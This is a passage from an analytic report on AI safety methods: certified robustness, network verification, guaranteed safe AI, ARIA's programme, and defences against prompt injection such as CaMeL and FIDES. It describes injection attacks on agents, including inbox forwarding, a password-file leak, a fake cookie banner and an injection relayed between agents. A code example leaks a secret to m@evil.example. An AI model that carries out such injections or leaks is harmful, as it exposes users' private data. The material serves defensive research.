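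Their method, randomized smoothing, works with any classifier. It makes many copies of the picture, adds random noise to each, and returns the label that the classifier gives most often. Let s be the standard deviation of the noise, with colour values running from 0 to 1, and let p be a lower bound on the share of noisy copies that get the top label. If p is more than a half, the top label stays the same for every altered picture within a distance of

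R = s × Φ⁻¹(p),

where Φ⁻¹ is the inverse of the standard normal distribution function. With s = 0.5 and p = 0.99, Φ⁻¹(p) is about 2.33 and R is about 1.16. The distance between two pictures is the square root of the sum of the squared differences in their colour values.

The theorem holds because the noisy copies of the original and altered pictures overlap heavily, so the classifier's labels for the two groups cannot differ much. Cohen and colleagues worked out the worst classifier compatible with p. If the attacker moves the picture a distance d, the share of noisy copies to which that classifier gives the top label falls from p to Φ(Φ⁻¹(p) − d/s), which stays above one half as long as d is less than R. In the example, a change of size 1 lowers the share from 99 percent to 63 percent at worst, so the label stays the same.

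Engineers estimate p by sampling because nobody can calculate it exactly for a large network. If 1,000 noisy copies all get the same label, then by the rule of three p is at least 0.997 with 95 percent confidence, and R is about 1.37. The rule works here because the engineer chooses the noise, although it is usually unreliable against attackers. The theorem then extends the result from the random samples to every attack within R, with the same 95 percent confidence.

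However, the pictures it covers are all very similar. A distance of 1 is enough to change one colour value from the minimum to the maximum, or a thousand values by 8 steps out of 255. A distance of 1.16 allows a change of less than one step per value if it is spread evenly over all 150,528 colour values of a standard picture. Shifting a photograph sideways by one pixel looks harmless, but if that typically changes each value by 5 percent of its range, the distance is about 19.

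The guarantee also doesn't ensure that the label is correct. On ImageNet, a large collection of photographs, the best smoothed classifier for a distance of 1 labelled 57 percent of pictures correctly, but only 37 percent had a label that was both correct and guaranteed to that distance. For a distance of 3, the share both correct and guaranteed was 12 percent.

This kind of guarantee covers only prompts that closely resemble the original, so it doesn't cover most jailbreaks. Someone who rewrites a forbidden request as a story, for example, may change every word of it.

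### Bounding a network layer by layer

Network verifiers prove that every input in a chosen set gives an output with a stated property. The set may be a small region around one picture or a range of physical measurements. The usual technique is bound propagation, which works out layer by layer how large or small each neuron's value can get.

Here is a small example, adapted from one that Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026) give in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism*. Two inputs, x₁ and x₂, lie between −1 and 1. They feed two neurons,

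a = max(0, x₁ + x₂) and b = max(0, x₁ − x₂),

and the network's output is a + b. Many real networks use the same max(0, ·) step, called a ReLU. Suppose the output must never exceed 2.5.

The method that needs the least computation bounds each neuron separately. Both x₁ + x₂ and x₁ − x₂ lie between −2 and 2, so a and b are each at most 2 and the output is at most 4. This bound is correct but too loose to prove the property, because a reaches 2 only when x₂ = 1 and b only when x₂ = −1.

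A better method keeps track of how each neuron depends on the inputs. For y between −2 and 2, max(0, y) is never above the straight line (y + 2)/2. Therefore

a + b ≤ (x₁ + x₂ + 2)/2 + (x₁ − x₂ + 2)/2 = x₁ + 2 ≤ 3.

The x₂ terms cancel and the bound improves to 3, which is still not enough to prove the property. The verifier then has to split the problem into cases by which neurons are above zero. If both are, the output is 2x₁, which is at most 2. If only one is, the output is x₁ + x₂ or x₁ − x₂, also at most 2. If neither is, the output is 0. The maximum is therefore 2, and the property holds.

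Two neurons give four cases, and n neurons can give 2ⁿ. Good verifiers split only where necessary, but exact verification of ReLU networks is NP-complete, so no method is fast on every network unless P = NP. Some finer estimates of the difficulty assumed the Exponential Time Hypothesis, which said that the logic problem 3-SAT needs exponential time. Those estimates lost their support when OpenAI's AI refuted the hypothesis in October 2026, but the NP-completeness result doesn't depend on it.

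The faster methods avoid the rapid growth in the number of cases but give looser bounds in deeper networks. To save memory, Vorobyov and Ilyushin used the least demanding method for some neurons in their test networks. The final bounds hardly changed in a two-layer network, but in a six-layer one they were off by more than 700.

### How large a network can be

Verification tools compete every year on a common set of problems. A correct answer earns 10 points and a wrong one loses 150, since a false proof is much worse than no proof. Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues (2025), in *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)*, describe 25 sets of problems, including these:

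| Network | Parameters | Property to prove |
|---|---|---|
| Aircraft collision avoidance | 13,000 | Rules for the output over ranges of five measurements |
| Two small vision transformers | 68,000–76,000 | Same label if each colour value changes by at most 1/255 |
| Wear of aircraft parts | 60,000–262,000 | Predicted remaining life stays in a stated range |
| VGG-16 image classifier | 138 million | Same label after changes to one pixel, several or all |

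The organisers set these problems, but that does not mean any tool solved all of them. VGG-16 is a large network, but the easiest problems set for it change only a single pixel. In 2026 Vorobyov and Ilyushin completed a proof for an image classifier from the 2024 competition by splitting the network's weights between two graphics processors. Classifiers of this type have a few million parameters.

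Chatbots are transformers, and the entry for transformers is far less impressive. Its two networks have two and three layers and label about 60 percent of pictures correctly, because their designers kept them shallow and narrow so that the tools might be able to verify them. A language model with 7 billion parameters, small by current standards, is about 90,000 times the size of the larger network.

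The smallest network in the table probably has the most useful properties. Its five inputs are physical quantities that an engineer understands, so a theorem can establish a property that matters for safety across a whole range of flight situations. A network that classifies pictures has 150,000 inputs that mean little individually, so engineers prove only that small changes to a picture don't change its label.

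### Proofs based on how a model works

Bound propagation doesn't require knowing what a network has learned. In *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability*, Gross, Agrawal and colleagues (2024) asked whether such knowledge would make proofs shorter. Mechanistic interpretability is the attempt to work out a network's algorithm from its weights.

Researchers trained 151 tiny transformers to pick the largest of four numbers between 0 and 63. Each model had one layer and about 8,300 weights, and their average accuracy was 99.92 percent. The researchers aimed to prove that a model's accuracy, averaged over all possible lists of four numbers, is at least some figure b.

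The obvious proof is to run the model on all 64⁴, or 16.8 million, lists. Gross and colleagues shortened it by using how the models work. A model gives about 3.4 times as much attention to a number as to the number one below it, then copies whatever it attends to most. From this, they showed that a model does no worse on a list than on the worst of certain simpler lists made from that list's numbers, each with at most three different numbers, so the proof has to check only the simpler lists.

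| Proof | Computing steps | Accuracy proved |
|---|---|---|
| Run every list | 2⁴⁷ | 99.92% |
| Check lists with at most three different numbers | 2²⁵ | 95.31% |
| Use more of the explanation | 2²¹ | 70.2% |

The second proof is about four million times shorter than the first, and its bound is less than five percentage points weaker. The third is shorter still, but its bound is much weaker. Every explanation leaves out some part of the weights that looks like noise, and a proof must assume that this noise does as much damage as possible.

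In a deep network, those pessimistic assumptions build on each other. *Interactions between crosscoder features* (2026) gives the rule for a model whose layers an explanation describes imperfectly. If εₗ is the largest possible error after layer l, then

εₗ ≤ Kₗ × εₗ₋₁ + eₗ,

where Kₗ is the most that the layer can stretch a difference between two inputs, and eₗ is the new error that the explanation adds there. If every layer could at worst double a difference, thirty layers would multiply an early error by about a billion. The real errors may stay small, but the proof can't assume that.

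People also had to write the earlier proofs by hand for each model and task. *Interactions between crosscoder features* shows how, in principle, to generate a proof from a crosscoder, a second network that describes the activity in all of a model's layers with a single set of features. The researchers tried this on a 33-million-parameter model that writes simple stories. The bound was informative for some single layers, but for the whole model it was so loose that it ruled nothing out.

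For now, the method may be more useful for checking explanations than for proving safety. *Evaluating Explanations* (2025) presents it as a test of explanations, because a more faithful explanation of a model allows a shorter proof or a tighter bound. Even with the 95 percent result, the model could still fail on one list in 21. The proof does not show which lists those are, and an attacker would look for them.

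Max Tegmark, a physicist at MIT, describes another way to use interpretability in his talk *Provably Safe AI*. His group trained a network to add numbers, used an automated tool to extract its algorithm as a Python program, and proved that the program adds any numbers correctly, including ones outside the training data. The proof covers the Python program, and it extends to the original network only if someone also proves that the two always agree. Nobody knows how to extract a readable program like this from a chatbot.

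### Guaranteed safe AI

A third approach is to prove that a system's actions will keep the world in an acceptable state, whatever happens inside the network. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple et al., 2024) sets out a framework for this, with a world model that describes what could happen after each action, a safety specification that defines which outcomes are acceptable, and a verifier that checks a proof that the system's actions meet the specification in that model. Dalrymple and colleagues argue that, above some level of risk, developers should have to show that their systems have such guarantees.

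In an invented example, an AI decides each morning how many packs of a drug a hospital pharmacy should order. In the world model, patients use at most 40 packs a day, and each order arrives two mornings later. The specification requires that the pharmacy never run out. The AI may choose any order size to reduce waste, as long as the packs on the shelves and on order total at least 120 right after it orders.

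Two mornings later, everything on order has arrived, and patients have used at most 80 packs. At least 40 are left, which is enough for that day. If the pharmacy starts with 80 packs on its shelves, this argument covers every day and every pattern of demand in the model. A monitor can check each order by simple addition, and a backup rule can top up any order that is too small, so nobody has to prove anything about the AI itself.

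The number 120 is a trivial example of a certificate, but no number that simple will work for a neural network that controls a power grid. In *Safeguarded AI* (2026), the plan for a British research programme on this approach, Nora Ammann proposes learned certificates. One kind is a Lyapunov function, which works like the energy of a swinging pendulum with friction. If its value always falls, the system must settle down. An AI can train a network to serve as this function, and checking it takes far less work than finding it.

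Deliveries are sometimes late, so a realistic world model has to include probabilities. If one delivery in 100,000 is late, the chance of a shortage in a given year is at most 365/100,000, or under 0.4 percent. The proof of that bound is certain, but it assumes the rate of late deliveries, which someone has to establish from delivery records. By the rule of three, showing that late deliveries are that rare would take about 300,000 punctual deliveries in a row, or more than 800 years of daily deliveries to one pharmacy. Pooling the records of many pharmacies would help if their suppliers were alike.

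### ARIA changes course

Ammann's £59 million programme belongs to the Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a funding body set up by the British government. The original 2024 plan was to have AI manage systems such as energy grids and supply chains under mathematical guarantees. ARIA hoped this would persuade governments to let powerful AI act only through "gatekeepers" that check its proofs.

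The programme has since moved towards software. In ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), David Dalrymple, its first director, says he stopped a competition to select a team to develop specialised AI for the work. He would probably have chosen no team, because he expected ordinary AI models to gain most of the necessary skills anyway. ARIA moved the £18 million to tools for writing and checking proofs. It then cancelled a second round of funding for physical applications, although existing projects could finish. Ammann adds that timely international agreement on gatekeepers had become less likely.

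By December 2026 ARIA was spending £22 million on eight cybersecurity projects, with goals ranging from containing AI agents to protecting code on Android phones, according to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*. Further teams can apply for £2.5 million to £3.5 million each, and Innovate UK Business Connect's *ARIA* says that a red team will attack their products with AI tools. The programme is devoted to proof, but it also pays for failure search to check the results. Ammann cites an encouraging precedent from the American defence research agency DARPA, whose red teams spent a long time attacking systems that contained verified parts, including a manned helicopter. The verified parts, among them seL4, withstood the attacks.

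ARIA says it moved away from physical systems because AI is progressing quickly and cyber defence is urgent, and it wants to return to them as the tools improve. Its retreat therefore doesn't show that guarantees for physical systems are impossible. But the programme ends in 2027, so a convincing demonstration on something like a power grid now looks further off. Building a world model also takes a lot of work. In one earlier project, the team studying pharmaceutical supply chains interviewed more than 80 people in the industry, even though people wrote the rules that industry follows.

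### Can anyone model the world?

Tegmark and the computer scientist Steve Omohundro make the boldest case for proof. In *Provably safe systems* (2023), they call it the only path that guarantees safe and controlled AGI, meaning AI that can do most intellectual work at least as well as people. Their main argument is that even an extremely intelligent system cannot prove a mathematical falsehood. People therefore don't have to understand or trust an AI. They can require a proof of safety for every action it recommends, run a simple checker, and refuse any action whose proof fails. Tegmark and Omohundro expected AI to write these proofs, and it now does so for software.

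They also need people to be able to model physical, digital and social systems precisely. In *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024), Andrew Dickson disputes that they can. He argues that physics, chemistry and biology have nothing like a complete set of symbolic rules, and that even if they had, a prover would need accurate data about the initial state of the world, which would be very hard to get. He says that engineers have understood these limits for decades and finds it puzzling that leading advocates of verification mostly dismiss them.

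Biology is the hardest case, because proving that a new DNA sequence is harmless would require predicting what it does in a human body. Zac Hatfield-Dodds, an AI safety researcher, says in his talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* that formal models of biology would take something like a thousand years of progress in microbiology. Biologists don't yet know what much of human RNA does, and a full model would also involve quantum chemistry.

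Supporters of proof can reply that a world model can be incomplete as long as it is cautious. Civil engineers use simplified rules with generous margins to build bridges that stand for a century. The pharmacy proof needs an upper limit on demand but no theory of disease. A proof that a design follows the rules also has a social advantage, because a regulator or a rival country can check it without trusting the engineer.

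This is a good reply when a cautious rule still leaves room for useful work, but in biology it often doesn't. A company that makes DNA to order could make only sequences on an approved list, and a verifier could easily check that it did, but then nobody could use the company to develop a new vaccine.

The comparison with bridges also leaves out that an AI may search for plans. If it uses its world model to find the plan that takes the least time or resources, it will tend to pick plans that depend on the model's mistakes, even without bad intentions, because those plans look better than they are. Safety margins based on ordinary experience may then be too small.

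*On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes another objection, from the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, that a proof based on current physics could become irrelevant when physicists revise their theories. The objection matters little for bridges or pharmacies, since Newton's mechanics is still accurate enough for both, but it would matter more for a system able to discover new physics before people do.

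### Can anyone define harm?

An AI could meet the pharmacy's specification by ordering 10,000 packs every morning. It would never run out, but most of the packs would expire while other hospitals went short. A limit on the total stock would prevent this. Somebody may then notice that the AI buys from the most expensive supplier, or leaves nothing for an epidemic, and add more rules. Each rule comes from a failure that someone thought of or saw, so people improve specifications by a kind of failure search and, as in any such search, cannot be sure what they have missed.

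Language models are harder to prove safe because harm often depends on what happens after the answer. A nurse and a poisoner might ask the same question about a dangerous dose and get the same true reply, so no property of the text separates the two cases. A specification that forbade all answers about dangerous doses would also keep useful information from nurses.

Ammann suggests specifications that limit the probability of a harmful outcome relative to what it would be if the AI did nothing. This sensibly avoids blaming a hospital's AI for deaths that would have happened without it. Someone still has to list the harmful outcomes and decide how much risk is acceptable. People disagree about both, and a better theorem prover can't settle either. ARIA funds research on how the people affected should make these choices.

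### What cheap proofs leave to be done

With AI, writing proofs about software takes much less work, which removes an obstacle for other systems that already have a good model and a clear specification. AI can also look for certificates, such as Lyapunov functions, that people would struggle to find. As this work becomes easier, Ammann expects that people will mostly have to trust the specifications and assumptions. Dickson and Hatfield-Dodds think the knowledge needed for those is missing.

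A more basic obstacle for today's chatbots is that many of the theorems one would like to prove about them are false. By the time of Davies's account, AISI had broken the safeguards of every system it had tested. The statement "This model never helps with a biological weapon" was therefore untrue of those systems, and a sound checker would reject any attempted proof of it. Developers would first have to build a model for which the statement is true.

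Even a true statement may have no proof of manageable length. A prover that needs less computation still faces the explosion of cases in exact verification and the errors that build up in a deep network. The backdoor theorem of Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues sets a firmer limit. It covers simple models whose backdoors stay hidden even from someone who reads every weight. If an efficient prover could regularly prove clean models of this kind free of backdoors, it would distinguish them from backdoored ones, because it could never prove a backdoored model clean. The theorem rules this out. Someone who received only the finished weights therefore could not prove such a model clean, though a developer who trained it and kept extra evidence might be able to.

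Software has neither of the problems Dickson raises. Its world model is a description of a processor, which engineers designed to behave predictably, and "never crashes" is a short specification that hardly anyone disputes. Hatfield-Dodds likes the idea of using AI to produce verified software, but he says it is no substitute for work on the safety of AI itself. He also doubts that verified tools could compete with generally capable AI, so he expects people to keep building and using models that nobody has proved safe.

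## Can safety be built into the system around the model?

Developers can guarantee some properties of a system even if nobody has proved its model safe. A language model only produces text, and ordinary software controls which actions that text can trigger. For example, an email assistant with no tool for deleting messages cannot delete any, whatever its model writes.

Most designs of this kind defend against prompt injection, such as instructions hidden in an email. Willison, who named the attack, traces it to the user's request and the untrusted text reaching the model in a single stream. Training has not taught models to keep the two apart reliably, since attacks adapted to trained defences still get past them. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) starts from a stricter principle: once an agent has read untrusted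 text, that text must be unable to trigger any action with harmful side effects.

### An email assistant that sends a file

The best-known design is CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google DeepMind and elsewhere introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe its three main parts: a planning model, a quarantined model and an interpreter. Suppose Alex asks an assistant to send dana@example.com the report she requested in her last email. The planning model sees this request and a description of the available tools, but no emails. It writes a short program:

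```
mail = last_email_from("dana@example.com")
name = quarantined_model("Which file does this email ask for?", mail)
file = find_file(name)
send_email(to="dana@example.com", attachment=file)
```

The interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program. It fetches the email and stores it in `mail` without showing it to the planning model. The quarantined model reads the email and returns a file name. It has no tools, so it can only return a value.

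Now suppose Dana's email quotes a stranger's message containing a hidden instruction to forward Alex's whole inbox to another address. An ordinary agent would read the instruction while able to send email, and might follow it. In CaMeL the quarantined model may be completely fooled, but the program has no line that forwards the inbox, and the planning model wrote the recipient's address before the quarantined model read the email. This property, which security engineers call control-flow integrity, means that untrusted data can influence which planned steps run but cannot add new ones.

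The stranger can still try to change the data. The hidden text might persuade the quarantined model to return "salaries.xlsx" as the file name. CaMeL therefore attaches tags, called capabilities, to every value, recording where it came from and who may read it. A value z computed from x and y inherits the restrictions of both:

readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y).

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that checks the tags. Suppose the policy for `send_email` requires every recipient to be a permitted reader of the attachment. Alex and the personnel office may read the salary file, and Alex and Dana may read the email that led to its selection. Only Alex may read both, so the interpreter blocks sending the file to Dana. Dana may read the report she wanted, so the interpreter sends it. If the stranger names another file that Dana may read, she receives the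 wrong file, but no data leaks.

### Other ways to separate instructions from data

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe six design patterns, most of them simpler than CaMeL.

| Pattern | How it works | What hostile text can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | Nothing, if it arrives in the results |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before reading any data | Change the content of a planned email |
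| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and gives a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Make the answer about its own document wrong |
| Dual LLM | The planning model handles untrusted values by name only, and a model without tools reads them | Change those values |
| Code, then execute | The planning model writes a whole program, as in CaMeL | Change values that the program uses |
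| Context minimisation | The system deletes the user's prompt before the model writes its reply | Affect the steps before the deletion |

The last pattern protects against hostile users. A car buyer might try to talk a sales chatbot into a large discount. If the chatbot first turns the request into a database search and the prompt is then removed from its context, the buyer's arguments cannot affect the quoted price.

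Separating the models does not prevent leaks by itself. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) analyses a plain dual-LLM agent. An injection cannot add a tool call to the agent's plan, but it can make the quarantined model copy private notes into a reply that the plan was already going to send. The paper finds that CaMeL-style tags, which the plain agent lacks, let a monitor stop this.

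Tags come from information-flow control, a decades-old branch of computer security. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, an agent Microsoft built around it. FIDES plans one step at a time instead of writing a complete program, and keeps untrusted results in variables whose contents are hidden from its planner. The planner can open a variable, but FIDES then treats all the planner's later actions as influenced by untrusted data, and the policies block the sensitive ones.

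This flexibility helps when the right steps depend on the data. For example, a user might ask the agent to add a calendar event if any recent email proposes a meeting. The planner's next step depends on what the emails say, so FIDES can have the quarantined model read them and return only yes or no. A hostile email can make the answer wrong, but a yes-or-no answer leaves little room for new instructions. A request to do whatever is on a to-do list is harder, because the list supplies the instructions.

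### Tasks completed with and without the guarantee

AgentDojo, the usual benchmark for these designs, has 97 ordinary tasks in a simulated office, bank, travel service and Slack workspace, along with injected attacks. Debenedetti and colleagues reported that CaMeL completed 77 percent of the tasks, compared with 84 percent for an undefended agent, and used nearly three times as many tokens.

Later tests found larger losses. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on the bank tasks using two models, with and without its policy checks. Costa and colleagues compared FIDES with a basic agent, both using GPT-4o. The FIDES figures below are averages of their results for the four settings.

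| Test | Tasks completed without the policies | With the policies |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL on the bank tasks, Garby and colleagues | 67–71% | 37.5% |
| FIDES on all four settings, Costa and colleagues | 84% (basic agent) | 50% |

In return, the policies stopped every attack that counted as a real breach of them. In Costa and colleagues' test, the basic agent let through 152 injections and FIDES with policies let through none. Adding the same policies to the basic agent also stopped the attacks but lowered its average to 42 percent, so FIDES's hidden variables recovered part of that loss.

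*SecureClaw* (2026) reports that CaMeL completed even fewer ordinary tasks, 29 of 97, though it blocked all 629 attacks. The paper's own system completed 59. The researchers had to adapt CaMeL's released code to their test, which may have hurt its performance. Still, CaMeL's completion rates on this benchmark range from 30 to 77 percent, which suggests that the loss in completed tasks depends heavily on the model, the policies and the setup.

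Garby and colleagues' figures also show that CaMeL stops most attacks by separating the plan from the data. With the policy checks off, only 5 of 622 completed attack runs succeeded. In about two thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the attack needed a tool call that would never appear in the plan. Turning the policies on stopped the remaining attacks but cut the number of completed tasks by nearly half. AgentDojo's attacks are fixed, so these results may understate the policies' value. An attacker who knew the likely plan would target the data in it, which the policies protect.

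In many of the lost tasks, the agent has to read a bill and pay it. A policy based only on where data came from must either refuse the genuine bill or accept a forged one. Garby and colleagues built an agent, Randori, whose planner can declare in advance that a specific piece of untrusted data may be used for a specific purpose. Randori completed 75 percent of the bank tasks with GPT-5.2. Only 2 of 1,296 attack runs across three models succeeded, both with a forged payment request in a file that the user had told the agent to follow. Without such declarations, Randori blocked that attack too, but its completion rate with one of the other models fell from 75 to 62.5 percent.

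CaMeL seems to reduce task completion less for more capable models. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, tested teams of agents on industrial maintenance tasks and found that CaMeL lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Those two also needed CaMeL's protection least on a version of AgentDojo for teams. Without CaMeL, attacks succeeded 1.5 percent of the time against Fable 5 and never in 949 attempts against GPT-5.5.

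On these numbers, a developer with a strong model gives up much usefulness for little protection. However, the guarantee is meant for attacks outside the benchmark. Even for attacks in the benchmark, 949 failed attacks in a row are compatible with a success rate of 0.3 percent, by the rule of three.

### Counting the approvals as well

Microsoft researchers object that these comparisons undervalue the guarantees. In practice, careful companies make an undefended agent ask a person before each consequential step, and the benchmark scores don't count that work. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) therefore counts the approvals. An agent with labels has to ask only when an action would break a policy, and on AgentDojo this cut approvals by a factor of up to 1.5 with no loss of completed tasks.

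They then told the planner about the labels and policies so it could plan around them, which reduced approvals by a factor of up to 1.9. Their agent can also ask the user to vouch for a piece of data instead of approving each action. If an email contains a list of ten jobs, the user approves the email once rather than ten separate tool calls.

People should pay more attention to each question if they are asked fewer of them. But a mistake in approving the email is more serious, because a user who overlooks a hostile line in it has authorised all ten actions. Someone who sees the calls one at a time has ten chances to notice that something is wrong.

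### Gaps in the tracking

These guarantees hold only if the software tracks every route that data can take. Garby and colleagues found routes that CaMeL misses. In this simplified program, the user's bank balance is secret:

```
quiet = True
rich = True
if balance > 1000000: quiet = False
if quiet: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes `quiet`, and CaMeL tags it as secret because the change depended on the balance. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` keeps its public tag and the email goes out. If the balance is low, the fourth line sets `rich` to false and no email goes out. The recipient learns whether the balance is high, although no secret value reached the send tool. CaMeL adds a tag only on the branch the program takes, so it misses the information carried by the branch the program skips.

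CaMeL also retries a failed program in a loop outside the tracked part of the system. Each one can reveal one bit about a secret, depending on whether a policy blocks the attempt, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it. A trustworthy planner would rarely write such programs, so these gaps matter most if an attacker can influence the planner or the planner itself is untrustworthy.

Peters-Gill and colleagues found a gap that can arise with an ordinary program. They asked a coordinating agent to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. The coordinator got the data from a database agent and passed the summary to a notification agent, and all three agents ran CaMeL. The database contained a hidden instruction, which the coordinator copied into its request to the notification agent without its own planner seeing it. The notification agent's planner treated the whole request as trusted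 and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to an outsider.

Peters-Gill and colleagues also prove that any team of this kind with an untrusted data source can have its plans altered, even if each agent is secure on its own, if agents can pass on what they read as part of a request. In their fix, agents send instructions and data through separate channels, and the interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. The average attack success rate across the five models was 12.9 percent without CaMeL, 0.2 percent when each agent ran CaMeL separately, and zero with the fix.

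Agents that operate a computer through its screen are even harder to protect. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to these agents. The planner has no access to the screen, so it has to write a branch for everything that might appear there. Plans averaged about 40 branches, compared with about four for AgentDojo, and the system kept at most 57 percent of the leading models' performance.

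The plan's many branches give attackers a new target. A sensible plan includes a step that closes any cookie banner, so Foerster and colleagues put a fake one inside an advertisement. The agent followed its plan, clicked the banner and reached the attacker's site. Policies also help little here, because a click at the same coordinates may log the user in, delete a file or do nothing, depending on what is on the screen.

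### Products and extensions in 2026

Microsoft has started to offer these designs to developers. Its *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announces FIDES as an experimental feature of Microsoft's Agent Framework. In the example, an agent handles bug reports on GitHub, and a stranger's report contains an instruction to post the contents of a password file. The agent may obey and read the file, but the file's contents are labeled "private", so the software blocks the agent from posting them publicly.

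Developers have to label each data source themselves, and FIDES treats an unlabelled tool as trusted and public. A forgotten label therefore removes the protection without any warning. Microsoft says it is considering the opposite default, which would be safer but block more work.

GitHub's command-line coding agent also has an experimental version, though Microsoft's *Information-flow control* notes that it does not yet cover all tools. The labels can prevent honest mistakes as well. In Microsoft's example, an agent reads Priya's email with unpublished sales figures and Marco's email asking about them. A reply based on both emails may go only to Alex, who received both, so the agent cannot send Marco the figures on its own.

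Google has adopted controls outside the model in more than one form. Help Net Security's *Google’s $10,000 refund test shows why AI agents need zero trust* describes an open-source customer service agent that Google built on the assumption that the model could be compromised. UMass Amherst's *Bagdasarian's Contextual Agent Security Adopted in Google Cloud Gemini Enterprise* reports that a Google Cloud product now checks tool calls against the user's intent and rules written in plain language. This check might catch a forged bill that labels would let through, but it has to interpret what people meant, so it cannot offer the same kind of guarantee as comparing labels.

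Nikolaou and colleagues' extension of CaMeL checks the whole plan before anything runs. Suppose a company requires approval before anyone disconnects a computer from its network. CaMeL would detect a missing approval only when it reached that step, perhaps after hours of work. The extension turns the plan into a diagram of possible states and searches it for a path that breaks the rule. If it finds one, it sends the path to the planner, which tries again. The diagram simplifies loops, so the extension sometimes rejects a safe plan.

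### A proof that covers attacks nobody has thought of

All these designs depend on ordinary software, such as CaMeL's interpreter, and an attacker who took control of that software could ignore every policy. Formal verification can rule out such a takeover without anyone listing the possible attacks.

Engineers could place a small program, called a gateway, between an AI agent and the outside world, and prove that for every possible input it sends only files on a list that Alex has approved. As long as the theorem's assumptions hold, this proof also means that nobody can gain the ability to run arbitrary code of their own inside the gateway, whether through a buffer overflow or a trick that no human has imagined. If they could, they would be able to make the gateway send a file that is not on the list, which would contradict the theorem.

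The specification describes what the gateway may do. Proving that the gateway meets it rules out every method of taking full control, such as a buffer overflow, without listing them. An attacker with full control could make the gateway do something the specification doesn't allow. Even a weak specification is enough. A proof that the gateway never sends a file larger than ten megabytes would still rule out arbitrary code execution, since an attacker who could run arbitrary code could send a larger file. The argument holds however clever the attacker is, so it covers an AI agent that tries to break out. Unlike guaranteed safe AI, it needs no model of the outside world, because the specification concerns only what passes through the gateway.

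It does need several other things to be true:

- Everything in the trusted base has to be right, including the hardware. An attacker who can flip bits in the memory chips is outside the theorem.
- The gateway has to be the only way out. If the agent can also open web pages, it can put the contents of a secret file into a web address.
- The specification has to forbid the harm in question. An agent that may choose when to send approved files could encode a secret in the timing, and the theorem would still hold.

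Garby and colleagues have applied this kind of proof to an agent's control software, the program that calls the model. Their interpreter is written in Lean, and they prove, roughly, that secret data cannot affect what an outsider observes, except through whether the program finishes. This rules out leaks like the one in the bank balance example. As far as they know, nobody had verified such software before.

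### What the rules leave open

A hostile email can make the quarantined model write a false summary, such as one saying that sales rose when they fell. This misleads the user without changing the agent's steps or leaking a secret. Costa and colleagues call this a text-to-text attack and do not count it as a breach of their policies. These designs also do not prevent the agent from giving bad advice or manipulating its user, because it has to be allowed to talk to them. A manipulated user can then approve actions that the policies blocked.

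The rules also don't ensure that permitted actions are wise. If Alex lets an agent trade shares up to a limit, the agent can still lose that full amount on foolish trades. A lower limit would reduce the possible loss but also restrict what the agent can do.

Kolluri and colleagues defend against hostile data and state that they trust the user, the planning model and the tools, as earlier designs of this kind did. That trust matters most to anyone worried about the AI itself, because a planning model with harmful aims could write them into the plan, and the labels would mark that plan as trusted. One of FIDES's standard policies even allows private data to go to a new recipient when the decision to send it came from a trusted context. To guard against an untrustworthy planner, developers need limits that apply regardless of who made the decision, such as a cap on payments or the gateway's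 list of files. Those limits would also stop some legitimate work that the present policies allow.

How much usefulness to give up for safety therefore depends on the job. A customer service agent that chooses among ten fixed actions loses almost nothing under the action-selector pattern, so there is little reason to build it any other way. An agent that reads strangers' messages, holds secrets and can send data out should probably have these restrictions even if it completes a third fewer tasks, because a person can do the remaining tasks but can't undo a leak. Coding agents fall in between. Microsoft points out that an agent working only on public code, or only on private code, can usually run without interruption, and that the rules interrupt it mainly when it mixes the two.

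Microsoft advises developers to skip FIDES if the agent has no privileged tools and the worst case is "a wrong answer, not a wrong action". This is reasonable for prompt injection, since FIDES would have nothing to block. But a nurse who acts on a wrong answer about a drug dose can harm a patient even if the agent never calls a tool.

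## Does the lesson from software security carry over to alignment?

Alignment researchers, who work on making AI systems pursue what people intend, have long borrowed ideas from software security. An influential example is *Security Mindset and Ordinary Paranoia* (2017), a fictional dialogue by Eliezer Yudkowsky of the Machine Intelligence Research Institute (MIRI). It contrasts two kinds of caution.

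Ordinary paranoia means imagining attacks and blocking each one. A programmer who fears that someone will steal a file of passwords might encrypt it and hide the key elsewhere on the disk. Using seven hidden keys would add little, since an attacker who can read two of them can probably read them all. The deeper solution is to store only a one-way hash of each password, a scrambled version that is easy to compute and impractical to reverse, and to compare hashes when someone logs in. A thief who reads the file still cannot log in, so security no longer depends on keeping attackers from reading the disk.

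Yudkowsky wants every system to have a "simple, solid story" about why it is secure, with few assumptions, all of them factual. "Nobody can guess the password" is too vague. An engineer could instead assume that every password has 50 bits of randomness, that the system accepts one guess per second on each connection, and that an attacker has at most 300,000 connections for a month. The attacker could then try about 0.8 trillion of the 1.1 quadrillion possible passwords, which gives about a one in 1,400 chance of guessing the right one. Anyone who doubts this conclusion can dispute a specific assumption.

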